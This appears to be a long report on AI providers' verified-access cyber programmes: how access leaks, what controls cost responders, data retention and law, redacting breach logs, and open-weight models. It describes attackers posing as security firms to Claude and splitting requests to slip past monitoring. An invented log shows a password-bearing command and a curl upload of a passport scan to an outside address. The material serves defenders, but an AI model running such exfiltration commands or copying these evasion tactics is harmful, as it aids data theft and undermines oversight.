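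A related complaint is that access checks favour large firms with plenty of paperwork. Anthropic's requirements for Red Team Access partly support this. An in-house team can show that its company takes security seriously with the relevant part of an annual report, a formal security certificate, or a bug bounty programme that has paid outsiders for reporting flaws for at least a year. Large companies generally have these already. A small testing firm without an accreditation must have been registered for at least a year and employ at least two testers with recognised certificates. Two excellent responders who left a large company to start such a firm would therefore not qualify in its first year.

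The complaint is weaker for incident response, because Defense Access requires little more than proof of identity, a description of the work and decent account security, which a small company can manage. The harder part is knowing that the programme exists and having someone apply before a breach.

Both companies let individuals apply for access, which helps independent researchers and open-source maintainers. Individual access is less suitable for responding to a breach, because Anthropic's individual approval covers only the person who holds it, and an employee who pastes an employer's breach data into a personal account creates a new problem.

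Another option is to deliver the model's results through a security vendor. Anthropic's *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* (2026) argues that the greatest risk comes from direct access to a model, and that a customer who receives only a patch or an alert is much less able to misuse it. Anthropic is therefore building Mythos into security vendors' products. OpenAI counted more than 35 such products and partner services by September. A company that already pays one of these vendors can get help the same day without applying, but only with the tasks the product or service covers.

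The providers have also promised money and practical help. OpenAI's *Daybreak for Frontline Defenders* (2026) commits $1 billion in subsidised access, training and support, which OpenAI hopes defenders will use within six months. Priority recipients include water and electricity suppliers, local governments, community banks and nonprofits. One pilot trains members of MS-ISAC, an association through which American state and local bodies share threat information. Anthropic (2026) announced free security scans for open-source projects and a programme that sends engineers to infrastructure operators' sites. It has also set aside $35 million in credits for open-source security.

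Most of this pays for finding and fixing flaws before an attack. That may well prevent more harm than help after one would, but it doesn't address the complaint about emergencies, and the freight company isn't in any of the priority groups. A billion dollars of subsidised access, valued at OpenAI's own prices, also costs OpenAI less than that, and defenders with few staff may not be able to use their share in six months.

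Neither provider's help page describes a faster review for an organisation with an intruder in its network. OpenAI did act quickly on its own initiative after attacks on American water systems, offering the affected states and utilities Daybreak access, technical help and up to $1 million in credits. A little-known company can't count on such an offer. A published emergency route, perhaps with access that expires after a week, would address the complaint more directly. But it would also attract attackers posing as breach victims, and reviewers would have very little time to check their claims.

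## How verified access leaks, and the controls that limit it

Misuse leakage occurs when capability meant for defenders reaches attackers. Attackers can pose as breach victims or steal an approved user's account or key. An approved user can also misuse the access or share it. A supplier working for the provider may leave a way in, and a customer may build the model into a product that outsiders can use. The best-documented leak so far involved a supplier and an insider.

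### The unauthorised access to Claude Mythos Preview

A handful of people in a private online forum got access to Anthropic's Mythos Preview on April 7, 2026, the day the company announced the model's limited release, according to Bloomberg's *Anthropic's Mythos Model Is Being Accessed by Unauthorized Users* (2026), which relied on documents and an unnamed source. The group used a Discord channel for gathering information about unreleased AI models. According to The Next Web's *Unauthorized users gained access to Anthropic's restricted Mythos AI model*, the group gave Bloomberg screenshots and a live demonstration.

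One member of the group that gained unauthorized access to Anthropic's Mythos model worked for an Anthropic contractor. Quiroz-Gutierrez (2026), in *A group of users leaked Anthropic's AI model Mythos*, writes that the group guessed the model's location from Anthropic's past practices, which it knew about from data that hackers had taken from Mercor, an AI training startup. According to The Decoder's *Unauthorized users breach Anthropic's restricted Mythos AI model*, the group also used the contractor's credentials. It probably found the model by guessing, then used the credentials to get in. Jeff Brown, an expert quoted in IANS's *Unauthorized Users Have Already Gained Access to Anthropic's Mythos* (2026), described the breach as a basic supply chain problem that only looked like an AI problem.

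The group reportedly used Mythos regularly for harmless tasks, not for cyberattacks. It also claimed to be using other Anthropic models. Anthropic said it was investigating a report of access "through one of our third-party vendor environments". It said it had no evidence that its core systems were affected or that the activity went beyond that environment.

The group still had access when Bloomberg published its story. VKTR reported during the investigation that Anthropic had not confirmed how the group got in, whether the group still had access, or whether it had used the model's offensive capabilities. Anthropic doesn't appear to have published its findings. In June it extended the programme to about 150 more organisations and set security requirements for them, according to *Expanding Project Glasswing* (2026).

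David Lindner, the chief information security officer at Contrast Security, told Quiroz-Gutierrez that thousands of people probably had access through the first 40 or so companies, so a leak "was bound to happen". The incident is not evidence for his other conclusion, that China must already have the model. It shows that a provider can vet its customers carefully and still leak access through a contractor. The group never applied for access, so better checks on applicants would not have stopped it.

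### False applicants

Fortune (2025) reported that the operators of the GTG-1002 espionage campaign told Claude they were a legitimate security firm doing defensive testing. Lying to a verification programme takes more work than lying to a model. Anthropic prefers evidence it can look up in a public registry or certification directory, wants the name on it to match the applicant's, and warns that a LinkedIn profile or a screenshot usually isn't enough.

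This should stop people who can't back up their claims. It is less useful against a group that can register a real company or recruit someone with a clean record, because proof of identity doesn't reveal intent. Such a group would find Defense Access easier to get than Red Team Access.

### The trade in stolen accounts

Many criminals would rather buy an account than apply for one. Kirk (2026), in *Inside the underground market for AI access*, describes sellers offering AI access at discounts that sometimes reach 70% to 90%. Kirk works for Okta, which sells account-security software and so has a commercial interest in the problem, but some of the figures are specific enough to be useful.

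Some leaked access comes from infostealers, malware that copies login data from an infected computer. The most useful data to steal are API keys and session tokens, which keep a browser signed in. An attacker who loads a stolen session token into another browser skips the login page and any second check, such as a code or a security key. Okta examined a collection of stolen data from 5,871 infected machines in 162 countries, released on Telegram in August 2026. It held thousands of unexpired session tokens for major technology and AI companies, and dozens of working API keys. The number of AI accounts is uncertain because the tokens for Google, Microsoft and Amazon came from sign-in systems that also cover many other services.

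Thieves ran up a $25,000 bill for one software architect, and an organisation's bill reached nearly $1 million before anyone contained the fraud.

Other resellers open their own accounts to collect free credit. One, called Poison Claude, gathered $100 bonuses from Amazon's cloud service and passed its customers' prompts on to Anthropic's models. A configuration error revealed that it had nearly 900 active users. At an AI video company, Okta logged more than 105,000 sign-up attempts in one month from 251 network addresses, an average of more than 400 per address.

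Verified access makes this second business much harder, since every fake account would need an identity document and, for individual OpenAI users, a physical key. But it may make theft more attractive, because a verified account can do more than an ordinary one. Kirk doesn't say whether any of the stolen accounts had verified access or what a verified account would sell for.

Providers can cut off a thief once they notice the theft. After thieves used infostealer malware to hijack some Claude accounts, Anthropic signed the users out, which cancelled the stolen sessions, and removed their saved payment methods, according to Paubox (2026). Anthropic didn't disclose how many accounts the thieves had entered or what they had done there.

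### Products that pass the access on

A customer can also leak access by accident. Suppose the freight company runs a chatbot that answers questions about customs papers on the same OpenAI account its security team uses. If an administrator turned on Daybreak for the chatbot's project, anyone visiting the company's website might be able to ask security questions of a model with looser safeguards.

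OpenAI therefore restricts Daybreak to internal projects. Anthropic will consider a product built on Defense Access if its users can't direct the model or see its raw output, but it doesn't yet accept applications for products whose users can prompt the model. Approval on Anthropic's Team plan covers every user, so a company on that plan can't separate internal work from work for customers.

### Attacks through verified accounts

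There is no publicly confirmed case of an attacker using a verified-access account. The Mythos group came closest, but it reportedly attacked nobody and got in through a contractor. According to The Next Web's *Anthropic details how Claude was misused for surveillance and weapons*, the only case involving Fable or Mythos models in Anthropic's September misuse report was distillation, which means training another model on their answers.

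This is only mildly reassuring, because Anthropic's report ends in August, before the company opened its Mythos models to ordinary applicants. Misuse of a verified account may also be harder to spot, since the provider expects the account's owner to ask about malware and exploits routinely.

### What the controls cost responders

Each control below limits some kinds of leak and makes some part of incident response harder.

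| Control | Leaks it limits | Cost to responders |
|---|---|---|
| Identity and business checks | False applicants | Days of waiting, and refusal of some honest applicants |
| Physical security keys | Stolen passwords and login codes | A lost key can lock the user out |
| Short-lived API keys | Stolen keys | Scripts stop working unless someone renews the keys |
| Seat limits | Insiders and stolen accounts | Extra helpers may have no access |
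| Permitted network addresses | Keys and sessions used from elsewhere | Requests fail from home or a client's office |
| Separate workspaces | Products that pass access on | More setup, and refusals for anyone in the wrong workspace |
| Monitoring across sessions | False applicants, insiders and stolen accounts | False alarms, and the provider keeps more data |
| Removal | Any leak the provider has found | A mistake can cut off a team during a breach |

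None of these controls would have blocked the contractor's route to Mythos if Anthropic had applied them only to customers. The provider has to give its suppliers separate credentials, limit each credential to the models the job requires, and assume that outsiders will guess a model's address.

OpenAI requires individual users to sign in with a physical key that follows the FIDO2 standard. The key responds only to the genuine website, so a fake login page can't capture anything reusable. OpenAI also turns off password login and codes sent by email or text message. A user who loses every sign-in method and the recovery keys may never get the account back, so it makes sense to keep a spare key outside the office. The key doesn't protect a session that an infostealer copies after login.

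Anthropic currently requires Defense Access users to replace their API keys at least every seven days. Under that rule, the ShinyHunters affiliates who used one victim's key for about three weeks would have needed at least two more keys. The rule also means a response team can't store a key for emergencies, because it would expire within a week. From December 15, 2026, Defense Access won't allow API keys at all. Anthropic recommends workload identity federation, in which a program proves its identity through the system it runs on and receives a temporary credential. A team that uses a log-analysis script should move it off API keys before that date and check that it still works.

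Restricting access to approved network addresses is effective against thieves who try to use stolen access from elsewhere. OpenAI requires this restriction for API access to GPT-6 Cyber, its most restricted security model. During a breach, though, the freight company might disconnect its own network, and responders working over a phone connection would then be locked out of the model. The company can avoid this by registering a backup connection in advance. The restriction also fails if the intruder is already on a machine inside the approved network. Responders should use the model from a clean laptop. When they replace the other credentials the intruder could have reached, they should also replace the company's AI keys and end its AI sessions.

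Seat limits matter because each additional user might misuse the access or lose control of an account. If each person has a 0.2% chance of having their account stolen in a year, a team of five has about a 1% chance of at least one theft, while a team of 75 has about 14%. Red Team Access adds background checks and requires devices that the organisation controls. A company would struggle to arrange either for a freelance malware analyst hired on the first night of an incident.

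Monitoring is the main protection against someone who passed every check honestly and later became an attacker. It has to connect requests across conversations to catch attackers who split up their work, as GTG-1002 did. By default, Anthropic requires that its staff be able to review requests its automated systems flag, so it has to keep some of what responders send.

A provider that finds misuse can remove one user or a whole organisation. Anthropic reserves the right to narrow or withdraw access at its sole discretion if it sees activity that breaks its policies. Removing whole categories of users is much less precise. When Mythos was suspended in June after a US export order, the European Union's cybersecurity agency, ENISA, lost access, while early testers such as Cisco and the industrial security company Dragos kept theirs (Constantin, 2026, *Early users of Anthropic's Mythos still have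 access after US order*). Nothing public links the order to the April incident, but a provider that suspended a whole tier in response to a leak would cut off its honest users too.

### An illustrative count of leaks

The numbers in this example are invented, because no provider publishes the real ones. Suppose a programme receives 20,000 applications, and 200 of them (1%) are hostile. Its checks stop 95% of the hostile applicants, so 10 get in. The checks also wrongly refuse 990 (5%) of the 19,800 honest applicants, leaving 18,810 honest accounts. If thieves take over 0.2% of those accounts in a year, that adds about 38 leaks.

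So theft produces nearly four times as many leaks as false approval, although the order depends on the assumptions. The two would be about equal if any one of these changed:

| Assumption | Starting value | Value at which the two are equal |
|---|---|---|
| Hostile applicants stopped by the checks | 95% | 81% |
| Hostile share of applicants | 1% | 3.7% |
| Honest accounts stolen in a year | 0.2% | 0.05% |

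Kirk's figures can't settle the last of these, since they count infected machines without saying how many customers the AI companies had.

Counting days of access instead of accounts can also reverse the order. The owner of a stolen account may notice a strange bill within weeks, but an account opened by a false applicant has no honest owner to complain. If the 10 false applicants keep their accounts all year, they have 3,650 days of access between them. If thieves keep each of the 38 stolen accounts for three weeks, they have only about 800 days. The thieves would have to keep each account for more than three months to match the false applicants' total.

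If the provider tightened its checks to stop 99% of hostile applicants, and those checks also refused 15% of honest ones, only 2 hostile applicants would get in. Thefts would fall to about 34 because there would be fewer honest accounts to steal. Total leaks would drop from 48 to 36, but the provider would refuse another 1,980 honest applicants, or 165 for each leak avoided. Halving the theft rate through better account security would prevent about 19 leaks without refusing anyone else. Responders would still face some lockouts and expired keys, but they can prepare for those in a quiet month.

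### What a leaked account is worth to an attacker

Those 48 accounts would not all be equally dangerous. A leak does harm only as far as it gives the attacker marginal uplift.

A verified-access tier for malware analysis usually gives attackers little. They rarely need help to understand their own malware, and Hugging Face decoded its intruder's payloads with an open-weight model. A criminal might use the tier to take apart someone else's malware and copy its methods. But the Russian group that rebuilt its malware until security products stopped detecting it had no known verified access.

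Exploit development is different. In OpenAI's own test on advanced security requests, a stolen Blue account would have raised the share completed by half a percentage point over what the public could get from GPT-5.6 Sol. A stolen Red account, with its specialised model, would have raised it by more than 93 points. Taken literally, that is nearly 190 times the gain from a Blue account. The ratio is very rough, since half a point could easily be chance and an attacker can also use other companies' models, but even allowing for both, a Red account would add far more than a Blue one.

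An attacker's gain from leaked access also depends on skill. According to CyberScoop, Anthropic argued in its September report that AI had removed the skill advantage state-sponsored hackers once had over lone criminals. If so, ordinary and stolen accounts have already given attackers much of the benefit, and a leak from a verified tier adds only what those accounts couldn't do. For an expert, that may be mostly speed. Tom's Hardware notes that some older models can find many of the same bugs as Mythos, but more slowly and possibly less well.

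A tier's name is an imperfect guide to its risk. Defense Access includes Anthropic's Mythos models and lets users validate vulnerabilities, which can come close to writing an exploit. A leaked Defense account might therefore be worth more to an attacker than a leaked Blue account, even though both are entry tiers.

OpenAI promises "controls that scale with risk" in its plan for cyber defence, and the arithmetic supports that approach. Refusing 165 honest applicants to prevent one leak is very hard to justify for malware analysis, where a leak would give attackers little and the applicants may have an intruder in their network. It could be reasonable for exploit development, which fewer responders need.

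Even for a single exploit, the uplift to an attacker changes over time. Just after the file-transfer software's maker releases a patch, many servers are still vulnerable and working exploits may be scarce, so an account that can produce one is valuable to an attacker. Once a reliable exploit is public, producing another gives an attacker almost nothing new. A provider could therefore let responders in the lower tier reproduce exploits that are already public, which would often be enough for requests like the freight company's to test its patch.

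## Deciding what breach data may leave the organisation

A hosted model can analyse only the evidence that a response team sends it. When the freight company's responder pastes in four days of logs, the provider receives a copy of everything in them. How long the provider keeps that copy depends on the model, the account and the contract. Hugging Face avoided this by keeping its data on its own machines, but a team that relies on a hosted model has to decide what to send.

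### What breach data contains

Breach data tends to be more sensitive than a company's ordinary records because attackers look for sensitive information. The logs show which passwords the attacker used, and the copied files are the ones the attacker thought were worth stealing.

| Breach data | If the provider's staff read it | If a court demands it | If someone steals it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Working credentials | A dishonest employee could log in | Little harm once the company has revoked them | A second break-in |
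| Personal data, such as passport scans | More strangers see it | The other side's lawyers see it | Fraud against the people concerned |
| Clients' secrets, such as prices and suppliers | Possible breach of contract | A client's competitor may learn of them | Lost business and claims from clients |
| Unpatched flaws | More people know a way into other companies | The flaw may become public before the patch | Attacks on everyone who runs the software |
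| Lawyers' findings about fault | A weaker claim that they are confidential | Evidence against the company | Material for extortion |

Storage by a provider matters mainly because it makes the other three events possible, although some client contracts prohibit it outright. How long the danger lasts depends on the data. A password that the company revoked on Monday is nearly worthless to someone who steals it on Tuesday, but a passport can stay valid for ten years. A promise to delete everything after a month therefore protects the passport much more than the password, which should have been revoked by then.

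### Why providers want to keep records

Some customers have zero data retention, a provider's promise not to store prompts and answers after processing a request. Safeguards can still inspect each request as it arrives, but they can't compare it with earlier ones.

Axios' *OpenAI previews zero-retention safety system as Anthropic requires data logs* reports an example from Aleah Houze, OpenAI's head of product policy, in which someone asks about a weakness in a company's software in one conversation and about remote access or what security tools can detect in another. Either conversation could be ordinary research, but together they may be preparation for an attack. Stored records help to reveal such patterns. They also help to expose thieves who use a customer's stolen key and people who send hundreds of slightly different versions of a forbidden request in the hope that one gets through.

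Houze's example fits a responder's questions during a breach equally well, so a reviewer is more likely to see breach data than most business data.

### Who held the records in 2026

Since June 9, 2026, Anthropic has kept prompts and answers for 30 days on its Mythos and Fable models, including for business customers who previously had zero data retention. According to Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models*, staff can't read the conversations by default. A small group of approved reviewers can do so in certain cases, such as when an automated system flags something, and each access is recorded in a log they can't alter. Anthropic deletes the data after 30 days unless its systems have flagged it or the law requires keeping it. Anthropic calls flagged cases rare, but they may be much more common among teams that paste in live exploits, so responders shouldn't count on deletion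 after 30 days.

Anthropic expected the policy to be unpopular and to put business at risk, especially if competitors didn't follow, and OpenAI didn't. OpenAI's *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (August 19, 2026) previewed Private Safety Processing, in which automated systems look for patterns across stored conversations that OpenAI's staff can't open. According to The Next Web's *OpenAI previews Private Safety Processing to keep zero data retention*, the Wall Street Journal read the preview as a bid for customers unhappy with Anthropic's change.

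With zero data retention, stored conversations stay on infrastructure that the customer controls. When the system detects a risk, the customer gets the full alert, while OpenAI learns only the category and severity of the activity, which it can use to decide whether to act against the account.

In September Anthropic announced a similar arrangement, Enterprise Frontier Safeguards. Anthropic's *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers* credits more than 100 customers with helping to design it, many in industries whose rules restrict who may see their data. Conversations can stay in the customer's cloud account, encrypted with the customer's keys. Anthropic's software scans recent traffic there and sends alerts to the customer. Storage, keys and fully automated review are separate options, so Anthropic's staff could still review conversations if a company turns on only the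 storage.

The system entered public beta in November, as Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Anthropic wants to catch rogue AI activity without retaining your data*. It packages each alert as a "Safety Case" that contains no prompts or answers, so an analyst must look up the original conversation in the company's own storage. Eligible organisations can use it through Anthropic's platform, Amazon or Google, with Microsoft to follow.

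| Arrangement | Who holds the data | Who holds the keys | Who reviews flags | What the provider's staff learn | Status in December 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's 30-day retention | Anthropic, or Amazon or Google on some of their services | The company storing the data; eligible customers can add their own | Approved reviewers | Flagged content | In force on Mythos and Fable models |
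| OpenAI's zero data retention with Private Safety Processing | Customer | Customer | Customer; OpenAI decides on enforcement | Category and severity | Needs OpenAI's approval |
| OpenAI's Private Retention | OpenAI | Customer, according to the August preview | Automated systems | Category and severity, unless the law requires human review | OpenAI can apply it to particular customers and models |
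| Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, all options on | Customer | Customer | Customer | Not specified in the announcement | Public beta for eligible organisations |

OpenAI promised a technical white paper with the September rollout, and its current documentation cites one. Under that documentation, OpenAI can also give a customer written notice that a model is no longer eligible for zero data retention and apply Private Retention, which keeps the customer's conversations encrypted on OpenAI's machines. If OpenAI considers it reasonably necessary to investigate or prevent a severe risk, it can instead apply Safety Retention, under which its staff may read whatever the classifiers flag. Private Retention also has an exception for legally required review. OpenAI couldn't carry out such a review alone if only the customer had the keys, so a customer should ask who else can decrypt the data.

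The two companies' positions are much closer than they were in August. Both now accept that someone must keep the conversations, and both offer to let the customer do it. "Zero data retention" used to mean that nothing remained to be read, but with these systems it means that a record exists which the provider's software can read and its staff can't.

Customers largely have to trust the provider about that. In the talk *Improving Safety with Privacy*, Tetali, the engineer who leads OpenAI's work on such systems, proposes stronger guarantees. One is confidential computing, in which the hardware shields a running program even from the people who operate the machine. Another is remote attestation, which lets an outsider check what software the machine is running. Tetali also lists problems these designs raise, including appeals, incidents and software updates.

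Appealing a suspension could be particularly awkward for responders. Suppose OpenAI receives a signal marked "cyberattack, severe" from the freight company's account and suspends the account. Nobody at OpenAI can open the conversations and see that the company is the victim, so to get its access back quickly, the company may have to hand over some of the breach data the arrangement was meant to protect. It can prepare by agreeing in advance who may release material to the provider and keeping a redacted sample ready.

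Keeping the records in the customer's cloud is also risky if the intruder is in that cloud, because the stored conversations would show the attacker what the responders know and plan to do next. The records therefore belong in a separate cloud account with its own administrators and credentials. Help Net Security's *Anthropic’s Enterprise Frontier Safeguards lets your Claude logs stay in your cloud* points out that the customer also has to staff the alert queue. During a breach, that job falls to the same few people whose work is setting off the alerts.

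Sending alerts to the customer works well for catching a thief with a stolen key, because the key's owner wants to know. It works badly if the customer is an attacker who gained access through a false application, since the alerts would go to the attacker. OpenAI's limited signal at least partly addresses that case, because OpenAI can act on it without the customer's cooperation.

### Gaps in zero data retention

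A team with a zero data retention agreement can still leave breach data with the provider by using a feature the agreement doesn't cover. Under Anthropic's agreement, anything a customer uploads through the Files API stays there until the customer deletes it. OpenAI's agreement also excludes file storage, saved conversations and batch jobs. A responder with a 200-megabyte log will naturally want to upload it as a file, which would leave the log in the provider's storage.

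OpenAI may also keep an encrypted, partly processed form of a prompt on its machines for up to 24 hours so that it can answer a follow-up with less computation. If the model uses another company's tool, such as a service that looks up suspicious addresses, that company's retention rules apply to whatever the model sends it.

The agreement also covers only certain accounts. OpenAI doesn't offer zero data retention on its Free, Go, Plus or Pro plans, and by default it keeps business customers' API traffic for up to 30 days to monitor for abuse. An employee who uses a personal subscription because the company account is blocked loses any protection the company negotiated.

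### Retention under verified access

Verified access usually requires giving up some privacy. Anthropic requires data retention for everyone in its Cyber Verification Program, whichever model they use. Opus and Sonnet are otherwise available with zero data retention, so a team that joins to get fewer refusals from Opus loses that option for its verified work.

Organisations exempt from retention on Fable or Mythos can use the whole programme with zero data retention, but only for internal use. A response firm working for clients should therefore expect Anthropic to keep the clients' data. According to Anthropic's programme page, Enterprise Frontier Safeguards should offer eligible organisations an alternative once the system becomes generally available.

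In the Claude Console, retention and verified access both apply to individual workspaces, so a company can divide its work between two. Timelines and reports could go to an Opus workspace with zero data retention, because they contain many names and rarely need looser safeguards. Malware and payloads contain fewer names and often need looser safeguards, so they could go to the verified workspace. The division won't be perfect, because logs can also contain the exploit, and Claude may then refuse to process them in the first workspace.

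OpenAI approves zero data retention separately from Daybreak. A team that needs both should get written confirmation for each model it plans to use, since OpenAI can withdraw zero data retention from one model but not others. An individual with Daybreak Blue on a Plus or Pro plan can't get zero data retention.

### Data protection law and client contracts

Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the organisation that decides why and how to use personal data is the controller. A company that handles the data on its behalf is a processor and needs a written contract. In its *Data Processing Addendum* (2024), OpenAI agrees to act as its business customers' processor, including when it monitors for abuse. Sending personal data to a model under such a contract needn't be a new breach, but pasting it into a personal account without one could well be.

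Article 33 requires a controller to notify its regulator within 72 hours of becoming aware of a personal data breach, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. If the freight company establishes at 9 a.m. on Monday that someone has copied customer files, the notice is due by 9 a.m. on Thursday. The company may send what it knows and add details later, so the deadline isn't a good reason to skip redaction. In November 2025 the European Commission proposed extending the period to 96 hours and requiring a notice only for high-risk breaches, but it is safer to plan for 72 hours.

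A leak at the provider would be a separate breach. The provider would have to tell the freight company without undue delay. The company would then have 72 hours to work out whose data it had sent, which it can't do without a record.

When a response firm does the work, the client is usually the controller, the firm is its processor, and the AI provider is a sub-processor, which Article 28 allows only with the client's written authorisation. The authorisation can be general, but the firm must then tell the client about any new sub-processor and give it a chance to object, which is difficult during an incident. Anthropic's customers described the same burden, saying they didn't want another company holding their data because they would have to notify all of their own customers and update contracts. A response firm should name its AI providers and state the retention terms in the contract it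 signs before any incident.

Confidentiality clauses need a separate check, because they often protect information that isn't personal. Oakline, an invented client of the freight company, might accept a model seeing its shipping clerk's name but object strongly to its suppliers' prices leaving the freight company's systems.

A European company also has to consider where its data is processed. OpenAI offers to store and process API data in Europe for customers with approved retention controls. In several other regions, including the United Kingdom, it offers local storage but may process the data elsewhere. The approval takes time, so it is better to arrange it before an incident.

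### Privilege and court orders

After a breach, customers or shareholders may sue, and in the United States they can demand relevant documents. Attorney–client privilege protects confidential communications made to get legal advice. The work-product rule protects material that a party or its lawyers prepare because they expect a lawsuit. Neither protects the underlying facts, so the freight company would have to produce its original logs, and the dispute would normally be about whether it must also produce the analysis.

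Courts have often refused to protect forensic reports from disclosure. In 2020 a federal court in Virginia ordered Capital One to hand over Mandiant's report on the bank's breach. The bank's lawyers had formally directed the work, but Mandiant was already under contract to do much the same work, and the bank shared the report with about 50 employees, four regulators and an accounting firm. The court concluded that the bank would have commissioned a similar report without any lawsuit. In 2015 a court in Minnesota protected most of the material from Target's lawyers because the company had run two investigations, an ordinary one to learn what had happened and another to help its lawyers.

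Rulings on AI conversations are newer and have reached different results. In February 2026, in *United States v. Heppner*, a federal judge in New York held that a defendant's exchanges with Claude about his case were neither privileged nor work product. The defendant had used Claude on his own initiative, Claude was not a lawyer, and Anthropic's privacy policy allowed disclosure to the authorities. The judge suggested that the ruling might have been different if a lawyer had directed the work. The same month, in *Warner v. Gilbarco*, a magistrate judge in Michigan protected the ChatGPT material of a woman representing herself, reasoning that using a software tool is not the same as showing documents to an opponent.

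Neither case involved a response team or a business contract with confidentiality terms, so they give only rough guidance. Responders should assume that a court may one day read what they type. They should ask the model what happened and leave out speculation such as "was this our fault?" If the lawyers want AI help with questions of fault or liability, they should direct that work themselves in a separate workspace with restricted access, much as Target separated its investigations.

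A court can also override a provider's deletion schedule. In May 2025 a magistrate judge in New York ordered OpenAI to preserve output logs it would otherwise have deleted, because publishers suing it for copyright infringement wanted them as evidence. The order covered ordinary API customers uninvolved in the case. It didn't affect customers with zero data retention, since OpenAI had no logs of theirs to preserve. The duty to keep new logs ended that September, and the court later made OpenAI give the publishers 20 million ChatGPT conversations with identifying details removed.

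The newer systems weaken that protection in a different way. If the conversations are stored in the freight company's own cloud account, a court can demand them from the company. Once the company expects a lawsuit, US rules also require it to take reasonable steps to preserve relevant records, so it may have to switch off automatic deletion. Its lawyers should know that these conversations are stored before they promise that they have produced everything.

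### Preparing a log for a hosted model

The team should first sort its evidence into what it can send as is, what it can send after redaction, and what stays in-house. Published malware and the attacker's addresses can usually go unchanged. Logs normally need redaction. Lawyers' findings, complete copies of stolen files, and flaws that the software's maker doesn't yet know about should stay in-house.

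Before sending anything, the team revokes every credential that appears in the evidence, including session tokens and API keys, in case redaction misses one. If the company leaves an account active to watch the intruder, logs that might contain that account's password should stay in-house until the monitoring ends. The team should redact even revoked passwords, because people often choose a new password that resembles the old one.

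Next, a script replaces names with placeholders. Each name always gets the same placeholder, so the model can follow one account across thousands of lines. The placeholder also includes the thing's role, because LAPTOP_14 is more useful to the model than ITEM_14. The numbers should be random or arbitrary. If they were calculated directly from the names, anyone with a staff list could repeat the calculation and match them. The table linking placeholders to real names stays in-house, where a second script uses it to restore the names in the model's answer.

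Here is an invented entry from the freight company's logs:

```
03:12:09Z host=LT-KBRANDT user=svc-backup
cmd="net use Z: \\FS-03\Oakline Harbour!9x /user:svc-backup
& curl -T Z:\M_Silva_passport.pdf https://203.0.113.80/up"
```

Someone using the backup account on K. Brandt's laptop opened Oakline's folder on a file server, typing the account's password as part of the command, and then sent a scan of M. Silva's passport to an outside address. The short entry contains a credential, two people's names and a client's name. After redaction it reads:

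```
03:12:09Z host=LAPTOP_14 user=SERVICE_ACCT_3
cmd="net use Z: \\FILESERVER_3\CLIENT_7 PASSWORD_A /user:SERVICE_ACCT_3
& curl -T Z:\PERSON_22_passport.pdf https://203.0.113.80/up"
```

The outside address stays because it is an indicator of compromise. The commands stay too, so redaction won't make a refusal less likely.

| Question | Can the model still answer it? |
|---|---|
| What did the command do? | Yes |
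| What happened just before and after? | Yes |
| Which other machines did this account reach? | Yes, because its placeholder never changes |
| Did another account have the same password? | Yes, if that password always becomes PASSWORD_A |
| Was the password easy to guess? | No |
| Would this laptop's owner normally run backups? | Only if the team adds the owner's job |
| Did the attacker create an account with a lookalike name? | No |
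| Whom does the company have to notify? | No; the team looks this up in its own table |

The most serious loss from redaction is probably the ability to spot lookalike account names. Attackers sometimes create an account with a name like "svc-backups", hoping that nobody notices the extra letter that distinguishes it from the real "svc-backup". After redaction, the two names become SERVICE_ACCT_9 and SERVICE_ACCT_3, which hides the resemblance. The team can recover most of this information by having a script list all pairs of nearly identical names before redaction, then telling the model which placeholders replaced them.

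Simple scripts find names that appear on a list of staff, clients and machines, but they miss names in the text that aren't on the list. The team can look for those with Privacy Filter, a small open-weight model OpenAI released in April 2026 that detects and masks personal information in text and can run on the team's own machines. It is built for personal information, so the team still has to check for Oakline's prices separately.

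A person should check a random sample of the redacted log. If the reviewer reads 200 lines and finds no sensitive data, a common rule of thumb puts the upper limit on the share of lines that still contain some at 3 ÷ 200, or 1.5%, with 95% confidence. In a log of 40,000 lines, that could be as many as 600. A clean sample therefore supports sending the log only to a provider with good retention terms.

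Redacted data remains personal data for the company, because the company has the table that reverses the redaction. The EU's highest court held in September 2025, in *EDPS v SRB*, that such data may not be personal for a recipient who has no realistic way to identify anyone. That could reduce the consequences of a leak at the provider. However, a file path or an unusual job title may identify somebody, so the company should keep its processor contract.

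The team records who sent each batch, when, to which provider, model and workspace, and under what retention terms. It also keeps an exact copy of the redacted text. If the provider later reports a leak, the team can combine that copy with its table to find out whose data was involved within the 72 hours.

Redaction fails on evidence that the team can't yet read. Hugging Face's team could find most of the stolen secrets only after decoding the intruder's messages, so a redaction script would have missed them. If a hosted model had decoded the messages, its answer would have contained the secrets, and the provider would have stored them under whatever terms applied. The case for using a model on the team's own machines is strongest for encoded messages like these and for exploits of flaws that nobody has patched.

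## Running an open-weight model on your own machines

A team that runs an open-weight model on its own machines keeps its breach data in-house, and no provider can block its requests or suspend its account. But the model is somewhat weaker, and the team has to do the preparation itself. Hugging Face set one up in the middle of an incident, but few teams could do that, so it is better to do the work beforehand.

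### Choosing the model

*How Far Behind the Frontier are Leading Open Weight Models on Cyber?*, published in July 2026 by the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI), compares open-weight models with closed ones on security work. The open-weight model GLM-5.2 performed like closed models released 4 months before it on 70 short tasks, including reverse engineering and finding flaws in websites, and like those released 7 months before it on simulated attacks on whole networks. Through most of 2025, the gap was 6 to 10 months. In one simulated attack, which has 32 steps and would take an expert about 20 hours, GLM-5.2 kept pace with Claude Opus 4.6 until step 11 and then stalled.

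The US Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of NIST, reached a similar estimate in *Assessment of Z.ai's GLM-5.2* (2026). Newer open-weight and closed models have since come out. The research group Epoch AI put GLM-5.3 about six months behind in October, according to Barry in *Open-weight AI models are 6-7 months behind on cyber*. AISI's *Kimi K3.1 Pro performs comparably to Claude Mythos 5* (2026) found that Moonshot AI's newest open-weight model matched a June model from Anthropic on three new simulated networks, though neither completed the hardest one.

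| Evaluator | Open-weight model | What it measured | Gap behind closed models |
|---|---|---|---|
| AISI | GLM-5.2 | Security | 4–7 months |
| CAISI | GLM-5.2 | Security | About 4 months |
| CAISI | GLM-5.2 | Overall ability | About 6 months |
| Epoch AI | GLM-5.3 | Security | 6–7 months |
| AISI | Kimi K3.1 Pro | Simulated network attacks | About 5 months, counting from the release of its weights |

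Estimates of overall ability vary more. In May, Epoch AI put the average gap at four months, or 8 points on its capabilities index, which is roughly the difference between GPT-5 and GPT-5.5. The same month, CAISI (2026) estimated that DeepSeek V4 Pro was about eight months behind.

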